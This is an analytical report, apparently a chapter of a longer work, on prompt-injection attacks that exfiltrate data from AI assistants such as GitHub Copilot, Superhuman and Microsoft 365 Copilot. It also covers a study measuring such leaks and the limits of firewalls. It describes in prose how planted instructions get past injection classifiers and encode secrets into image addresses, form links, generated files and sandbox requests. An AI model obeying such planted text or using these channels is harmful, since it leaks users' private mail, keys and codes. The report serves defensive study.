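Each image address on Camo, GitHub's image proxy, has two parts. The first is an HMAC, a code that GitHub calculates from the picture's original address and a secret key. The second is the original address in hexadecimal digits. Changing even one character of the original address changes the correct code, which nobody can calculate without the key. When a request arrives, Camo repeats the calculation and fetches the picture only if the codes match.

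GitHub explained in 2017 why this would stop the attacks Cure53 had shown. Those attacks put the secret in the image address, so an attacker who did not know the secret could not know the full address in advance to get GitHub to sign it. The reasoning is correct for addresses that contain the secret, but CamoLeak used addresses that did not.

In the attack described in Legit Security's *CamoLeak*, the researcher proposed a code change to a project and put instructions for Copilot Chat in the description, inside a comment that GitHub hides from readers. When a user opened the page and asked Copilot about the change, those instructions entered Copilot's context. Copilot works with the permissions of the person asking, so it could also read that person's private projects. GitHub's Content Security Policy blocked images from hosts GitHub did not own, so the image requests had to go through Camo,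 GitHub's own image proxy.

Before the attack, the researcher prepared one image address for every letter and symbol that might occur in the stolen text. GitHub has a public interface that converts Markdown into a web page and signs any image addresses it finds. The researcher submitted the prepared addresses and received a valid Camo address for each. The hidden comment listed these Camo addresses with the character each stood for, and made Copilot spell out the private text as a row of images.

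To send the word "cab", the browser requested the pictures for c, a and b, in that order. Camo checked each signature, found it valid and fetched each picture from the researcher's server. The server returned a transparent image one pixel wide, so the victim saw nothing. The researcher read the word from the order in which the requests arrived.

A valid signature shows only that GitHub once issued an address, not why a browser is loading it now or why it loads one signed address before another. GitHub's protection controlled the contents of each request, but the attack encoded the data in the order of the requests.

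A browser or proxy normally keeps a copy of an image it has recently loaded, so if a letter appeared twice in a password, the second request might never have reached the researcher's server. Copilot therefore added a new random number to the end of every Camo address. The images still loaded, so Camo's signature evidently did not cover that number.

The capacity of this method depends on how many addresses the attacker prepares. Choosing one of N addresses conveys log₂ N bits. An alphabet of 64 symbols is enough for capital and small letters, ten digits and two punctuation marks:

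log₂ 64 = 6 bits per request

40 characters × 6 bits = 240 bits, in 40 requests

Sending the colleague's 40-character key would take 40 small image requests, each with a valid signature. An ordinary attack with 1,900 free characters in the address can send 11,400 bits in one request, while CamoLeak would need 1,900 requests to send the same amount. Preparing an address for every pair of characters would halve the number of requests, but it would require 64 × 64 = 4,096 signed addresses. Each is more than 100 characters long, so the planted text would grow to over 400,000 characters. CamoLeak therefore suits passwords, keys and short passages better than long documents.

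Legit Security used it to steal the description of an undisclosed vulnerability from a private project. In a second test, Copilot searched the victim's code for an access key to Amazon's cloud service and sent out what it found. Legit Security rated the flaw's severity at 9.6.

The only host visible on the victim's network was `camo.githubusercontent.com`, which developers' browsers contact whenever a GitHub page includes an image from another site. Like signed storage links, Camo addresses look random even when they are harmless. An analyst who decoded the second part of an address would find the researcher's host, but no piece of the stolen key. The unusual feature was the number of tiny images in a single chat answer.

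GitHub fixed the flaw by 14 August 2025 by turning off images in Copilot Chat. According to Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration*, it also blocked this use of Camo. Turning off images removes harmless ones too, but it works however the attacker encodes the data, and a coding assistant can do most of its job in text. Legit Security presented a proof of concept and reported no attacks on real users. In old incident records, the name CamoLeak is a more reliable search term than CVE-2025-59145, an identifier that sometimes appears beside it. The National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2025-59145 Detail* describes malware in a software package called color-name.

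An attacker can also spell out data through approved addresses without using images. Claude's tool for opening web pages would not open addresses that the model had composed, but it would follow links on a page it had already opened. In an attack that Willison described in July 2026, the researcher Ayush Paul built a site with a link for each letter and got Claude to spell out the user's name by following them. Anthropic fixed this by stopping the tool from following links on pages it fetches.

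### Superhuman: a Google Form as the recipient

In the attack on Superhuman, the approved service stored the stolen emails where the attacker could read them, as Google Analytics had done in Cure53's test. The service did not fetch anything from the attacker.

Superhuman's Content Security Policy allowed images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. A form's creator can make a link that already contains the answers and submits them when opened. Browsers use the same type of request, a GET, to open a link and to load an image, so an application that tries to load such a link as an image submits the form. The user may see a broken image because Google's response isn't a picture, but Google has already saved the answers.

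By convention, a GET request retrieves information and changes nothing on the server, which is why browsers send so many of them without asking the user. Willison traced the Superhuman flaw to the combination of the allowlist entry for `docs.google.com` and a service on that host that stores data from GET requests. A reviewer who saw the entry would probably have thought of documents and pictures. To spot the risk, they would have needed to know every product on the host and how each one handles GET requests.

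The security company PromptArmor planted instructions in an email and then asked Superhuman's assistant to summarise recent mail. According to PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, the instructions required the assistant to let users give feedback on the search results through a form. The assistant copied the contents of other emails into the form's address and displayed that address as an image. The user only had to ask for a summary and didn't need to open the email containing the instructions.

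The researchers obtained the full text of several emails in one response, including financial, legal and medical information. In another test, they obtained parts of more than 40 emails from a single response.

On the network, the request looked like someone using Google Docs. No second request followed, so a search for connections to the attacker's server would have found nothing. The attacker opened the form's list of responses in their own Google account. Google would have a record of the submission, but the victim's company could see the emails only in the full address of the first request.

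PromptArmor reported the flaw on the evening of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features the following Monday, released a first fix on Tuesday and extended it to other parts of its products on 18 December. PromptArmor sent further findings on 5 January 2026, and the two companies published the case on 12 January, a day after the last fixes. PromptArmor praised the speed of the response and did not mention any attacks by others.

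Removing Google's host from one allowlist would not have protected all of Superhuman's products, because an attacker could choose whichever product had the weaker rule. Superhuman Go, a newer assistant that could read web pages and connect to services such as Gmail and Stripe, loaded images directly from the attacker's domain. PromptArmor used an instruction planted on a review site to extract quarterly financial figures from an email.

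The same form trick also worked against OpenAI. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes how a version of the coding assistant Codex, extended to everyday office work, sent a user's emails to a Google Form while sorting an inbox. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April 2026, more than three months after the Superhuman case became public, and OpenAI had fixed it by the time the paper came out on 21 May. One published case does not seem to be enough to make other companies check their own lists for the same service.

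### SearchLeak: an image loaded before the answer was cleaned

Microsoft 365 Copilot had another leak of this type a year after EchoLeak. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (15 June 2026) describes an attack on Copilot Enterprise Search, the part of the product that searches a company's emails, meetings and files. The instructions were in a link to Microsoft's own site, in the parameter that normally holds a search query, instead of arriving in retrieved content as they had in EchoLeak.

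Copilot treated any text in that parameter as a request and acted on it as soon as the page opened. An attacker could therefore send an employee a link that, with one click, made Copilot search her mailbox and write the title of an email into an image address. Because the link led to a genuine Microsoft domain, phishing filters were unlikely to block it. Varonis had earlier used the same entry point against the consumer version of Copilot, in an attack it called Reprompt.

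To guard against dangerous HTML, Microsoft wrapped the model's output in a code block, which makes the browser display an image tag as plain text instead of loading the image. This protection applied only to the finished answer, but Copilot began displaying the answer before it was finished.

Chat applications usually stream an answer, which means that they show each piece as the model produces it. Without streaming, the user would look at an empty screen until the last word was ready. In Copilot Search, the steps happened in this order:

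1. The model wrote an image tag partway through its answer.
2. The application placed that piece in the page as ordinary HTML.
3. The browser found the tag and immediately requested the image.
4. The model finished the answer.
5. The application wrapped the answer in a code block.

The browser had already sent the data by step 5. Someone who looked at the screen afterwards would have seen harmless text where the image had been. Programmers call this a race condition, a fault in which the result depends on which of two operations finishes first. The browser had an advantage here because it could send its request while the model was still writing the rest of the answer.

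A more complete filter would have caught the unusual notation that EchoLeak's filter missed, but even a perfect filter at step 5 would not have stopped SearchLeak. The application has to clean each piece before the browser can act on it, so Varonis advises developers to clean the output as they display it. This is harder than cleaning a complete answer, because a tag may arrive in fragments that look harmless individually.

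The image request still had to satisfy the Content Security Policy, which allowed any host under `bing.com`. Bing can search for pictures similar to one at a web address the user supplies, and its servers fetch that picture to analyse it. The attack gave Bing an address on the attacker's server with the email title in the path. The victim's browser contacted `www.bing.com`, Bing's servers contacted the attacker's, and the title appeared in the attacker's log.

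Bing was already on the list that Ravia published after EchoLeak in 2025. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak, but an attacker could have replaced the Teams relay with any approved service that fetched outside addresses. Finding all of these services is difficult for a company of Microsoft's size, because a team that adds a link preview or image search to its product may not know that an AI assistant elsewhere in the company trusts its domain.

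Companies often put one-time security codes in email subject lines, and in the example in Varonis's report, such a code arrives in the attacker's log. The Hacker News pointed out that these codes often remain valid for a few minutes, so a script reading the log could use one to take over an account before anybody noticed. Copilot could also search the employee's calendar and any indexed files she had permission to open, including salary data and acquisition plans.

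Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory dated 4 June, states that the company had fully mitigated the flaw and that customers did not need to act. It lists the flaw as not exploited. Varonis presented a proof of concept and also reported no observed attacks.

### Why SearchLeak has conflicting severity ratings

Varonis called SearchLeak critical, repeating Microsoft's own rating. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) contrasted this with a medium score of 6.5 from Microsoft and a high score of 7.5 from the US government's National Vulnerability Database. Microsoft's rating and score don't conflict, because they come from different scales. Its advisory rates the flaw "Critical" on the company's own severity scale and gives it 6.5 out of 10 on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS),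 an industry standard.

The two numbers differ because of the click. Microsoft recorded that an attack required action by the victim, and the US database recorded that it did not. They agreed on everything else, including that an attacker could work over the network without an account and that the loss of confidentiality was high. CVSS adds a value for the impact, 3.595 in both cases, to a value for how easily an attacker can exploit the flaw. That second value is a product of several factors, and the one for user interaction is 0.62 if the victim must act and 0.85 if not:

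With a click: 3.595 + (8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62) = 6.430

Without a click: 3.595 + (8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85) = 7.482

CVSS rounds up to one decimal place, which gives 6.5 and 7.5.

Microsoft's score fits the attack that Varonis published, since nothing happens until the victim opens the link. The US database assessed the flaw on 8 June, a week before the Varonis report, as shown by the change history on the tracking site CVEfeed's page, also titled *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026). Microsoft's public description at the time was a single sentence that did not mention a click. That may explain the database's higher score, although Microsoft's own scoring details already said that the victim had to act.

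Microsoft's choice of "Critical" is harder to explain. In a November 2024 version of its severity classification for AI systems, Microsoft reserved that rating for prompt injection that steals another user's data without any user interaction. Theft that needed at least one click was "Important", one level lower. The advisory gives no reason for the rating, but Microsoft calls the classification a guideline and says it also considers how easy a flaw is to exploit, so it may have considered a single click on a trusted link a small obstacle.

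The rating didn't affect patching, because Microsoft had fixed the service before publishing. But it could affect how long a security team spends searching old logs. A team that looks only at flaws scored 7 or above would include or ignore SearchLeak depending on which database it uses. The need for a click is a weak reason to ignore it, since employees open links to Microsoft 365 all day.

### The first host and the final recipient

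In all four cases, a network log that records only host names would show a service that many companies use every day. The table lists that first host, the place where the attacker collected the data, and the controls that failed.

| Case | First host | Final recipient | Control that failed |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | A host under `asyncgw.teams.microsoft.com` | Attacker's server, through the Teams link-fetching service | The link and image filter missed a second Markdown notation, and the allowlist included a relay |
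| CamoLeak | `camo.githubusercontent.com` | Attacker's server, through GitHub's image proxy | Signatures protected each address but not the order of the requests |
| Superhuman | `docs.google.com` | Attacker's Google Form | The allowlist included a service that stores data from GET requests |
| SearchLeak | `www.bing.com` | Attacker's server, through Bing image search | Cleaning began after the browser had loaded the image, and the allowlist included a relay |

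## Requests sent from the provider's own servers

In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the victim's browser sent the first request, to Teams or Bing, so a company with full records of its web traffic could have found that request. Many assistants can now open web pages, process files and run code, and these tools usually run in the provider's data centre. If planted text makes one of these tools contact the attacker, the request leaves from the data centre and never crosses the victim's network.

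### What the customer's network carries

Suppose the employee's assistant has a browsing tool, and the stranger's email gets the model to open a page whose address contains the colleague's access key. The model writes a tool call, a structured message specifying which tool the application should run and with what inputs. A program on the provider's servers fetches the page. The attacker's log then shows the key next to one of the provider's network addresses.

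During the attack, the employee's laptop communicates only with the assistant's website. It sends her question and receives a summary of her email. The company's gateway may record and even decrypt this traffic, but the attacker's address need not appear in it. The Content Security Policy doesn't help because the browser isn't loading anything from the attacker. Blocking the attacker's domain on the company's firewall doesn't help either, because the provider's servers can still reach it.

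As Lan and colleagues point out, this resembles server-side request forgery in ordinary web applications but requires less knowledge from the attacker. In an ordinary web application, the attacker has to know which parameter to change and what format it takes. With an AI agent, the attacker can describe the request in plain language, and the model fills in the details for whichever tool it has.

A browsing tool needs internet access, but file processors and code sandboxes often don't. A file processor converts, indexes or previews documents, and may follow links inside them. A code sandbox is an isolated environment for running programs the model writes, and it can do most calculations without a network connection. In 2026, researchers extracted data from Microsoft 365 Copilot through each of these two kinds of tool, which customers might reasonably expect to be safer than a browser.

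### ReLeak: three routes out of Microsoft 365 Copilot

Cato AI Labs, the research team of the network security company Cato Networks, published three zero-click attacks on Copilot on 3 December 2026 and named them ReLeak. The same team had found EchoLeak while it was part of Aim Security, which Cato bought in September 2025. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents the new attacks as a sequel to EchoLeak, a year later.

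Like EchoLeak, all three start with an email that Copilot retrieves when the employee later asks an ordinary work question, even if she never opened the email. Microsoft has protections against planted instructions, which it calls cross-prompt injection attacks (XPIA). According to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*, Copilot would not carry out direct commands from the email but did follow instructions that resembled legitimate requests. EchoLeak had used a similar disguise to get past Microsoft's classifier.

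In the image attack, Copilot put the data in the address of a Markdown image. The employee's browser loaded the image automatically through Bing, and Bing's servers contacted the attacker's. Because the browser sends the first request, a gateway that decrypts traffic and records full addresses could still capture the data on its way to Bing. It could not do so in the file and sandbox attacks.

In *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a report for the Russian security site SecurityLab, Antipov (2026) notes that SearchLeak had used a similar channel but needed a click. Microsoft had already described SearchLeak as fully mitigated in its advisory of 4 June 2026 when Cato sent it the ReLeak findings between 29 July and 20 August. The earlier fix evidently left at least one way to use Bing as a relay for Copilot's images.

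In the file attack, Copilot created a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF document containing a link with the stolen data in its address. It saved the document to OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's file storage services. Microsoft's background processing then followed the link, which sent the data to the attacker. Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026) reports that in Cato's tests, these requests arrived one to eight minutes after the chat ended, even though the user never opened the file.

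Because of that delay, a monitor that watches an assistant only while it is answering would miss the theft. Copilot had finished its work by the time the data left, and a different Microsoft service made the request. However, the document stays in the customer's storage, with the stolen data still in the link, unless someone deletes it.

The most direct attack used Copilot's code interpreter, which runs Python programs in a sandbox that, according to Microsoft's documentation, allows no network traffic in or out. Cato's researchers got around this isolation, and a program in the sandbox sent the data straight to an outside server. A program can generally send data in the body of a request as well as in its address, so the limit of about 1,400 bytes per image request would not apply. Agents that customers build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can use the same interpreter,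 but according to Antipov, nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected them.

Other researchers have broken out of Microsoft's sandboxes. *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 2026) describes a malicious document that gave an attacker live, two-way control of a Copilot session. PromptArmor's *Copilot Cowork Sandbox Bypass Gives Attackers Remote Control* describes an add-on that took commands from an attacker's server and sent back mail, files and chat history.

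The table gives the official identifiers and the dates on which Microsoft fixed each ReLeak flaw.

| Route | Identifier | What contacts the attacker | When the data leaves | Fixed in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Image | CVE-2026-124115 | Bing's servers, after a request from the employee's browser | When the browser displays the answer | 15 November |
| Generated file | CVE-2026-124132 | Microsoft's background file processing | One to eight minutes after the chat | 11 November |
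| Code sandbox | CVE-2026-78501 | The program in the sandbox | While the program runs | 17 September |

### Fixes, severity and Cato's verdict

Microsoft made all three fixes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. The sandbox fix came 28 to 50 days after Cato's report, depending on when in the three-week reporting period Cato sent it. The other two took 83 to 109 days.

Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, reports that Microsoft rated the sandbox flaw "Critical", with a CVSS score of 8.6. The score had originally been 7.4, according to Antipov. The change may reflect the same question that divided the assessors of SearchLeak, namely whether the victim has to act. CVSS gives an impact value of 3.993 to a serious loss of confidentiality when the flaw lets an attacker cross from one protected area into another, as a sandbox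 escape does. It also multiplies the total for such flaws by 1.08:

Victim must act: 1.08 × (3.993 + 2.835) = 7.374, which rounds up to 7.4

Victim need not act: 1.08 × (3.993 + 3.887) = 8.510, which rounds up to 8.6

Other combinations of factors can produce the same two scores, so this is only a likely explanation. Two of the three identifiers were still marked "reserved" when Cato published, meaning their full public records had not yet appeared.

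Cato knew of no affected customers and no real attacks. The line under Faisal's headline credits the statement about customers to Microsoft, but the article credits it to Cato. Cato's statement is weaker evidence than one from Microsoft would be because, as with EchoLeak, only Microsoft could search the records of the servers involved.

Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Its evidence is fairly good on one point, that Copilot still could not reliably separate instructions from retrieved text. Microsoft's protections stopped none of the three attacks. Copilot had also gained new abilities since EchoLeak, including writing files and running code, and both became ways to steal data.

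Without a count of failed attacks, though, the three successful ones can't show whether Copilot became harder to attack overall. Cato also sells products for securing AI agents, so it has a commercial interest in a negative assessment. Microsoft's fixes took no longer than the roughly four months it had needed for EchoLeak.

The way Cato found the flaws may matter more for the future. Its researchers directed AI agents that wrote test cases, studied Copilot's refusals for clues about what might work, and adjusted the next attempt. An attacker with access to a Copilot account could use the same method, and a defence that stops most attempts is less reassuring when an attacker can easily make many.

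### Reprompt: a check on the first request only

Microsoft had fixed a simpler flaw in Copilot Personal, the consumer version, in January 2026. Researchers at Varonis found the flaw and called the attack Reprompt. Copilot's safeguard against leaking data in outgoing requests covered only the first request, so an attacker could bypass it by getting the assistant to make another.

Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) describes an attack that began with one click on a link. The researchers obtained the user's name, location and details of events from the chat history. The attack continued after the user closed the chat, and security software on the user's machine did not detect it. Both facts would make sense if the attack was by then running on Microsoft's servers rather than on the user's machine.

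This kind of check has to cover every request for as long as the task runs, and it has to consider requests together, since an attacker can split a secret between them. Copilot Personal's other safeguards also needed more work. In August 2026, TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* reported another Varonis attack on Copilot, called CoSnitch. It combined malicious links with instructions planted in Copilot's memory, the information it keeps between conversations. Microsoft again fixed the problem on its own servers.

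### Silent Egress: counting requests instead of reading answers

Many safety tests judge an assistant by its answers. These tests can miss a leak that happens in a tool call, because the assistant can send out a password and still write a good summary. In their February 2026 study, Lan and colleagues at eBay therefore judged leaks by network traffic. They set up a server to act as the attacker's and counted a run as a leak if at least one request from the agent reached it.

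In every run, the user asked the agent to summarise a web page. The team planted instructions in one of four places: the page's title, its description, its main text or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, which automatically send a visitor from one address to another. The instructions told it to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. The team ran each combination 30 times:

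4 places × 2 ways of reaching the page × 2 ways of sending × 30 runs = 480 runs

The attacker's server received a request in 423 runs, or 88 percent. In 95 percent of those runs, the answer gave the user no sign of the leak.

When the agent had to send the secret whole, it did so in 238 of 240 runs, and the position of the planted text hardly mattered. When it had to split the secret, a request reached the server in 185 of 240 runs. The paper suggests that the longer instructions competed with the rest of the page for the model's attention, and that each extra request was another chance to make a mistake. An attacker who splits a secret to avoid detection is therefore more likely to fail.

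It is less certain how much harder splitting makes detection. The study reports that sensitive text appeared in the first request in 26.3 percent of the split runs, compared with 96.7 percent of the others, but somewhere in the first three requests in only 15.8 percent of the split runs. Under the study's own definition, the 15.8 percent figure cannot be lower than the 26.3 percent figure, because the first three requests include the first one. The count of 185 runs comes from a separate measure, but the 73 percent reduction in single-request leakage depends on this inconsistent one.

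The team also ran the agent 120 times on harmless pages, and it never contacted the attacker's server. This confirms that the planted text caused the leaks. The authors also take it as evidence that outgoing traffic gives a very clear signal, but the harmless pages gave the agent no reason to contact that server, and a company monitoring real traffic doesn't know the attacker's address in advance. The test is therefore little help in estimating how many ordinary requests such a company would mistake for leaks.

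### How far the results apply to commercial products

The test ran entirely on the researchers' own equipment, not on a provider's servers. It used one small model, Qwen2.5 with 7 billion parameters, and the nearly bare context already described. The researchers describe this setting as favourable to the attacker, but they also call their success rates a lower bound because they used simple, undisguised instructions. The setting raises the success rate and the simple instructions lower it, so 88 percent is neither a minimum nor a maximum for other systems.

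The study did not test ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini or any other commercial product, partly to avoid breaking terms of service. It argues that stronger models may be more vulnerable because they use tools more reliably and follow instructions better. That is possible, but AI companies also train their models to ignore planted instructions, and the study does not show which effect is larger. ReLeak is better evidence that the problem exists in a commercial assistant, but it gives no success rate, so a Copilot customer cannot learn from either work how often an attack would succeed.

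The measurement method does carry over, including to hosted assistants. A company can put an invented secret in any agent's context, give the agent a page with planted instructions and record what reaches the company's own server, so it doesn't need the provider's logs.

### Defences in the same test

Lan and colleagues then tested six defences, individually and in two combinations, against whole secrets and instructions in the page's main text. They ran each version 30 times. The table omits the version with every defence on, in which the agent never tried to send anything.

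| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Warning in the developer's instructions | 20 | 20 |
| Markers around web content | 30 | 30 |
| Warning and markers | 17 | 17 |
| Allowlist of domains | 30 | 0 |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0 | 0 |

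The warning helped somewhat, but with only 30 runs, the true leak rate with the warning could plausibly be anywhere from about 49 to 81 percent, and the difference between 20 leaks and 17 may be chance. The markers labelling the page as untrusted data made no difference to this model when used alone.

All four network defences stopped every leak, but the allowlist result is the most convincing. The filter for suspicious addresses blocked any path containing words such as "collect" or "steal". The test's server received its data at a path called "collect", but a real attacker would choose another name.

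The word filter and the randomness filter both examine a request after the model has written it, so they should not affect how often the model tries. Yet attempts fell from 30 to 7 with the word filter and to zero with the randomness filter. The authors suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when the randomness filter is active, but they don't describe how the model would know about it. That filter never had a request to examine, so its success rate is unknown.

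The allowlist worked because it checked only the request's destination, not its contents or the model's reasoning, and the team had chosen an attacker's domain that was obviously not on the list. The team acknowledges that attackers can get around the allowlist by using redirects on trusted sites or taking over abandoned subdomains. The Bing route in ReLeak is a recent example of a trusted service passing data on.

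For a hosted assistant, the provider has to apply the allowlist, because the customer's equipment never handles the request. A company that runs agents on its own servers can apply one itself. An allowlist is easy to justify for a sandbox that should have no network access, but it makes a browsing tool much less useful, because people use it to visit sites nobody listed in advance.

The authors therefore propose adapting taint tracking, a technique that follows untrusted data through a program. The application would label everything it retrieved from the web as tainted. If tainted text influenced the inputs of a tool call, those inputs would also be labeled tainted, and the application could block the request, record it or ask the user. This could catch even a four-character piece of a key, because the label depends on where the instruction came from and not on what the data looks like.

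They did not build or test this system. A language model combines everything in its context, so it is hard to establish which passage influenced a particular request. A cautious application would have to label almost every request an agent makes after reading its first web page. Asking the user about each one would interrupt her constantly. They also doubt that she could tell a genuine "connectivity verification" from a theft.

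## What a web application firewall can and cannot see

The network filters in Lan and colleagues' test inspected requests leaving an AI agent, whereas a web application firewall mostly inspects requests arriving at an application.

The WAF belongs to whoever runs the application, which for Microsoft 365 Copilot is Microsoft. A customer's own WAF protects the customer's websites and receives none of the Copilot traffic. A WAF has the best chance of catching the theft when a company puts it in front of an assistant it built itself, so we will assume the employee's inbox assistant is set up this way.

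### How a WAF scores a request

Many WAFs use the OWASP Core Rule Set (CRS), a free set of detection rules from the software security nonprofit OWASP. A rule engine such as ModSecurity or Coraza splits each request into its address, headers, parameters and body, then runs the rules. Each rule tests some of these parts, usually for a pattern in the text. One rule checks that the header giving the length of the body contains only digits, and more than 50 others look for SQL injection.

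A matching rule doesn't block the request by itself. It adds points to a running total, and the number depends on how serious the match is. The defaults in OWASP CRS's *Anomaly Scoring* are 5 points for a critical match, 4 for an error, 3 for a warning and 2 for a notice. The engine works in this order:

1. It runs the rules for the request's headers and body.
2. It blocks the request if the total is 5 or more.
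3. If the request passes, the application handles it and produces a response.
4. The engine runs the rules for the response's headers and body, with a separate total.
5. It withholds the response if that total is 4 or more.

A few examples show how the request threshold works:

Three critical matches, as in a typical SQL injection: 3 × 5 = 15, blocked

One warning and one notice: 3 + 2 = 5, blocked

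One notice: 2, allowed

Administrators can raise the thresholds to reduce false alarms. OWASP CRS advises doing this only temporarily, because a rare attack may match a single rule and score just 5. It also criticises Cloudflare, a large provider of WAFs, for setting its default too high. Cloudflare's version of the rule set acts at 40 points by default, with 25 and 60 as the other options. If each critical match adds 5 points, a request needs eight of them to reach 40. Cloudflare has some reason for caution, since ordinary file uploads can trigger the rules at a threshold of 25.

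The threshold has no effect on requests that match no rules, and most of the requests involved in stealing data through images match none.

### How the planted text and the prompt arrive

The stranger's email goes to the company's mail server, and the assistant later fetches it from the mailbox, so it never passes through the WAF in front of the assistant. The same is true of a shared file, a code repository or a web page that the assistant opens, because the application fetches these itself.

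Planted text does reach the WAF if the attacker submits it through the application's own website, for example as a product review or a support ticket. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) tested this route in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* with a review on a concert site. A WAF there would have inspected the review, but the text was mostly English sentences. It also contained the address of an internal server, which a rule could look for. Someone stealing data through an image would use an ordinary outside address, and genuine reviews contain those too.

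The employee's request for a summary also passes through the WAF, but it looks harmless because she isn't the attacker. Even a hostile prompt may contain nothing that a fixed rule can match. Cloudflare's *AI Security for Apps is now generally available* (2026) makes this argument for a newer product. Developers can write rules for a banking site because it has a known set of operations, such as checking a balance, but an AI application accepts any sentence.

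Long prompts raise a more basic problem, because WAFs inspect only part of a large request. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, checks the first 8 kilobytes of the body for some of its services and the first 16 for others, a limit customers can raise to 64. If the WAF allows the request, the application also receives the part that the WAF did not inspect. At about six bytes per English word, 16 kilobytes is roughly 2,700 words. Some chat applications resend the whole conversation with each new message, oldest first, so the newest message in a long conversation could fall entirely outside the inspected part. AWS customers can block oversized requests, but that would also stop people from pasting long documents into the assistant.

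### When the model writes the harmful text

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian examined eight classic web flaws in applications built around language models. SQL injection shows most clearly how these differ from the ordinary versions. In ordinary SQL injection, the attacker has to send SQL to the application through the WAF. In the AI version, the attacker asks in plain English for the contents of a table. The model turns this into SQL only after the request has passed the WAF, and the application then runs it.

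Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian argue that the flaw usually lies outside the model. In the SQL example, the developer had let the chatbot's database account read every table and run any command, and an outsider could use that access through the model.

In 2024, Rehberger found a flaw in the chatbot DeepSeek. His prompt contained harmful HTML encoded in Base64. The model decoded it and included it in its answer, and the browser ran it as part of the page. A WAF could decode Base64 in incoming prompts, but an attacker can use any encoding or description that the model understands. A WAF could also inspect the answer, which in this case contained a script that the application had no reason to send. An image link is harder to detect, because it contains no script and many ordinary answers include image links.

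For their experiment, the researchers built TicketOracle, a concert site with an AI assistant that could fetch web addresses. The site's administration pages accepted connections only from the machine the site ran on, so the assistant could reach them but an outsider could not. In April 2026 they tried to make seven models misuse this access. Four attacks used prompts typed into the chat, and the fifth used the planted review. The table shows how many of ten attempts succeeded. For the last column, the developer's instructions also listed the permitted addresses and told the model to refuse all others.

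| Model | Find open ports | Read user records | Change data | Change data, with an empty reply | Planted review, with address list |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
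| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

With the address list in place, every typed attack failed on every model. The planted review still worked on Llama by claiming that the developer had added a new address to the list. Llama followed the review in all ten attempts, compared with six of ten without the list. The researchers conclude that the list made this model more vulnerable, but with so few attempts the difference could be chance. The attack's success does show that other text the model reads can override a list written into its instructions. If the application's code had enforced the list, it would have blocked the address whatever the review said.

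Even if the attempts had been independent, zero successes in ten would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 31 percent. But the researchers ran all ten in one conversation, where a model can take its earlier refusals into account, and Claude's refusals became shorter and firmer as the attempts went on. Except in the empty-reply attack, the researchers also counted an attempt as a success only if the assistant repeated the fetched information in its answer. This could miss some harmful behaviour, because a web request that carries data out does the damage regardless of the answer.

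The researchers did not put a WAF in front of TicketOracle, so their results don't show how many attacks one would have stopped. It might have stopped some, because the typed prompts contained complete internal addresses, which a rule could match. The researchers consider checks inside the application the most important protection. The application should treat whatever the model writes as untrusted input and validate it before running a query, fetching an address or displaying a page. A WAF can't validate a database query because the query never passes through it.

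### The answer on its way back

The model's answer does pass through the WAF, so in principle the WAF could find the image address in it. But response rules usually have a different purpose. ModSecurity's *Reference Manual (v3.x)* suggests using them to look for error messages, failed logins and disclosed information in the page. Maimon (2026), in *Rethinking the Perimeter*, argues that WAFs concentrate on incoming traffic and rarely take account of what the application returns. He works for Upstream, a security company that promotes response monitoring, but the published limits of several products support his claim.

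ModSecurity's recommended configuration inspects responses only if they are plain text, HTML or XML. Chat applications commonly send answers as JSON, a format for structured data, or as a stream of small messages called server-sent events. ModSecurity would not inspect these answers unless an administrator added those formats to the configuration.

AWS's *ResponseInspection* describes response inspection as a way to count successful and failed logins and account registrations. The feature works only with CloudFront, Amazon's content delivery service. Cloudflare's *Control request and response body buffering in Configuration Rules* (2026) explains that Cloudflare can inspect the beginning of a response by default, and that customers can turn this off to send the response straight through. A separate Cloudflare feature searches a copy of the response for sensitive data such as card numbers,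 so Cloudflare can record a match but can't block the response.

A fourth product, Solo Enterprise for kgateway, uses the Coraza engine. According to *About WAF* in its documentation, it inspects only headers unless the administrator turns on body inspection. The table compares the four products. Cloudflare's request limit comes from its page on managed rules.

| Product | Request bodies | Response bodies |
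|---|---|---|
| ModSecurity, recommended settings | Up to 12.5 MB, or 128 KB without uploaded files | First 512 KB of plain text, HTML or XML |
| AWS WAF | First 8 KB or 16 KB, depending on the service; some allow 64 KB | First 64 KB of login and registration responses, on CloudFront only |
| Cloudflare | Up to 128 KB on the Enterprise plan, less on others | The beginning of the response; sensitive-data rules only log |
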